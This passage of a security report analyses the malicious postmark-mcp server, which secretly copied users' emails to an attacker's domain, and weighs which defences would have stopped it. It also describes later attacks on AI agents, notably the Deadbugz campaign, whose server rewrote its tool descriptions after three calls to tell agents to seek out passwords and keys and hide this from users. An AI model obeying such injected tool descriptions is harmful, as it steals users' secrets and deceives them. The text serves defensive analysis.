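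Neither study estimates what share of MCP servers is malicious. Li and Gao counted 833 servers with exploitable flaws, which are sometimes dangerous to run, but such flaws are usually accidental. The count is also approximate, since four of the 41 flagged servers they checked by hand were false alarms.

### Which defences would have worked?

Installing the server only from Postmark would have prevented the copying. Semgrep pointed out that the genuine server on GitHub was safe. But it was hard to tell that npm was the wrong place to look, because Postmark had no package there to compare with phanpak's. Users had to start from Postmark's own website or documentation.

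Version pinning, which fixes the exact version to install, would have helped only people who had pinned a clean release. The newest available release was clean for about two days and malicious for about eight. Anyone who first installed the package during those eight days and pinned the current version would have pinned one that contained the BCC.

Pinning can also delay security fixes. He and colleagues describe serious flaws in Anthropic's own MCP server for the programming tool Git. Anthropic fixed them in a December 2025 release, but users who had pinned an earlier version would have kept the flaws until they changed it. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* therefore combines pinning with a review of every update. For postmark-mcp, a reviewer who compared version 1.0.15 with 1.0.16 would have seen an unfamiliar email address in plain text.

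**Waiting a few days** before installing new releases would have reduced users' exposure but not eliminated it. Tenable recommends waiting three to four days because, it says, researchers usually detect malicious packages within a couple of days. With a four-day wait, users could still have installed version 1.0.16 for about four days, starting on 21 September. A nine-day wait would have prevented them from installing it, because the package was gone by then.

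The value of waiting to install a new release depends on how quickly researchers publish what they find. If Koi's system flagged the change on 17 September, as its account suggests, an immediate public warning might have made even a three-day wait long enough. Tenable says npm has been adding checks on a package's age to its installation program, so users need not check it themselves.

Approval prompts would not have stopped postmark-mcp, however carefully the user read them, because the server added the BCC after approval. They are more useful against attacks like Invariant Labs' email experiment, where the attacker's address was in the tool call, but the user still has to see the address. Li and Gao found that three of the four assistants they tested hid the details of tool calls by default, and that all four let users allow tools to run without approval.

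In Croce and South's experiment, Claude Desktop asked for confirmation before each step, including the one that sent out the bank balance. They assumed that users would accept these prompts, but did not test this on anyone else.

Scanning tool descriptions would have found nothing, because phanpak's descriptions were accurate. Invariant Labs recommended storing a digital fingerprint of each tool description so that an assistant could detect later changes, but that would also have missed version 1.0.16 if Koi is right that only the BCC line changed. A fingerprint of the whole package would have changed, but it would also have changed with every harmless update.

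Comparing the code's behavior between versions is more promising, and Koi says this is how it found the package. But Koi published no figures on how often its system raises false alarms or misses malicious changes, so one success is not enough to judge the product.

Blocking giftshop.club on the user's network would not have stopped the copied emails, because Postmark delivered them. The log check that Snyk recommended could reveal a leak only after it had happened, but it was one of the few defences that did not require noticing the package in advance.

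Postmark has since changed its official server to identify its own traffic in Postmark's logs, along with the name and version of the assistant that connected to it. This should make unusual activity easier to trace. However, the label does not prove that the server is genuine, since someone who copied the code could probably copy the label too.

### Later attacks on AI agents

Other malicious MCP servers followed. *Deadbugz* (Fogel, 2026), a report for the company Pillar Security, mentions another MCP package that Koi found after postmark-mcp. That package started as a working tool, and an update then added backdoors.

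In August 2026, a campaign that Pillar named Deadbugz used the kind of attack seen earlier in the laboratory. Its malicious server offered two harmless text tools. A brief inspection would have shown only the harmless version, because the server changed its descriptions after three tool calls. The new descriptions told the agent to look for passwords and keys and to hide this from the user.

The attacker tried to spread the server through other people's software projects. On 10 August, a GitHub account called zellkernel proposed changes to 23 unrelated projects within 74 minutes. Seventeen of the proposals would have added the malicious server to a project's MCP settings. When Fogel reviewed them, 19 were closed, four were still open, and no project had accepted one through GitHub's usual process. Fogel reports no victims, and the campaign may have reached nobody.

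Deadbugz calls for different defences from postmark-mcp. The server in those 17 proposals ran on a remote computer, so users had no installed package to pin. Fogel recommends that assistants compare a server's tool descriptions with those the user approved, and ask for approval again if they have changed. This would help against Deadbugz, but it would not have stopped postmark-mcp's BCC.

An attack reported in September 2026 showed that installing software from its vendor does not always keep users safe. *MemTensor npm and PyPI Packages Compromised in Credential-Stealing Supply Chain Attack* (Zanki, 2026) describes malicious code in two packages for MemOS, a system that gives AI agents a memory. The code installed programs that stole developers' secrets. MemOS has a broader purpose than an MCP email server, but its users must also decide whom to trust.

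The MemOS package on npm had the developer's own prefix, @memtensor/, just as Postmark's official package now has @activecampaign/. Such a prefix offers no protection once an attacker can change the genuine package. Careful users could have discovered that Postmark had not published postmark-mcp, but checking the publisher of the MemOS package would have reassured them.

### How MITRE and OWASP recorded the case

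MITRE, a US non-profit research organisation, lists the Postmark case as AML.CS0053 in ATLAS, its public catalogue of attacks on AI systems. ATLAS also includes researchers' demonstrations, such as the extraction of AI models from the Google Photos app, so a listing does not by itself show that an attack had victims.

PromptRiskDB reproduces part of the Postmark record, which divides the attack into nine steps. One step describes how the attacker avoided scrutiny by waiting for users to adopt a clean version first, though the wait lasted only about two days. The record links to no entries in CVE, the standard public list of software vulnerabilities. CVE mainly covers flaws in legitimate software, so a count based on it, like that of He and colleagues, will generally leave out malicious packages.

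ATLAS classifies the case under AML.T0110, a technique for poisoned tools. The definition, as reproduced by PromptRiskDB, covers hidden logic in a tool's code as well as altered descriptions. This is broader than the usual meaning of tool poisoning, so the classification does not mean that postmark-mcp manipulated the AI.

In December 2025, OWASP, a non-profit known for its lists of common security risks, published a list for AI agents, the OWASP GenAI Security Project's *OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications for 2026* (2025). More than 100 specialists contributed to it. Its fourth item, ASI04, covers supply-chain attacks on agents. *OWASP ASI04 Explained*, a guide by Zealynx, a company that sells security audits, says OWASP uses the Postmark case in this item as its worked example of MCP impersonation. Koi's *OWASP Agentic AI Top 10* also says OWASP cites the case.

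"Impersonation" is the more informative label because it refers to the package's false association with Postmark. Users could have checked that association before installing any version, including those that did not copy emails.
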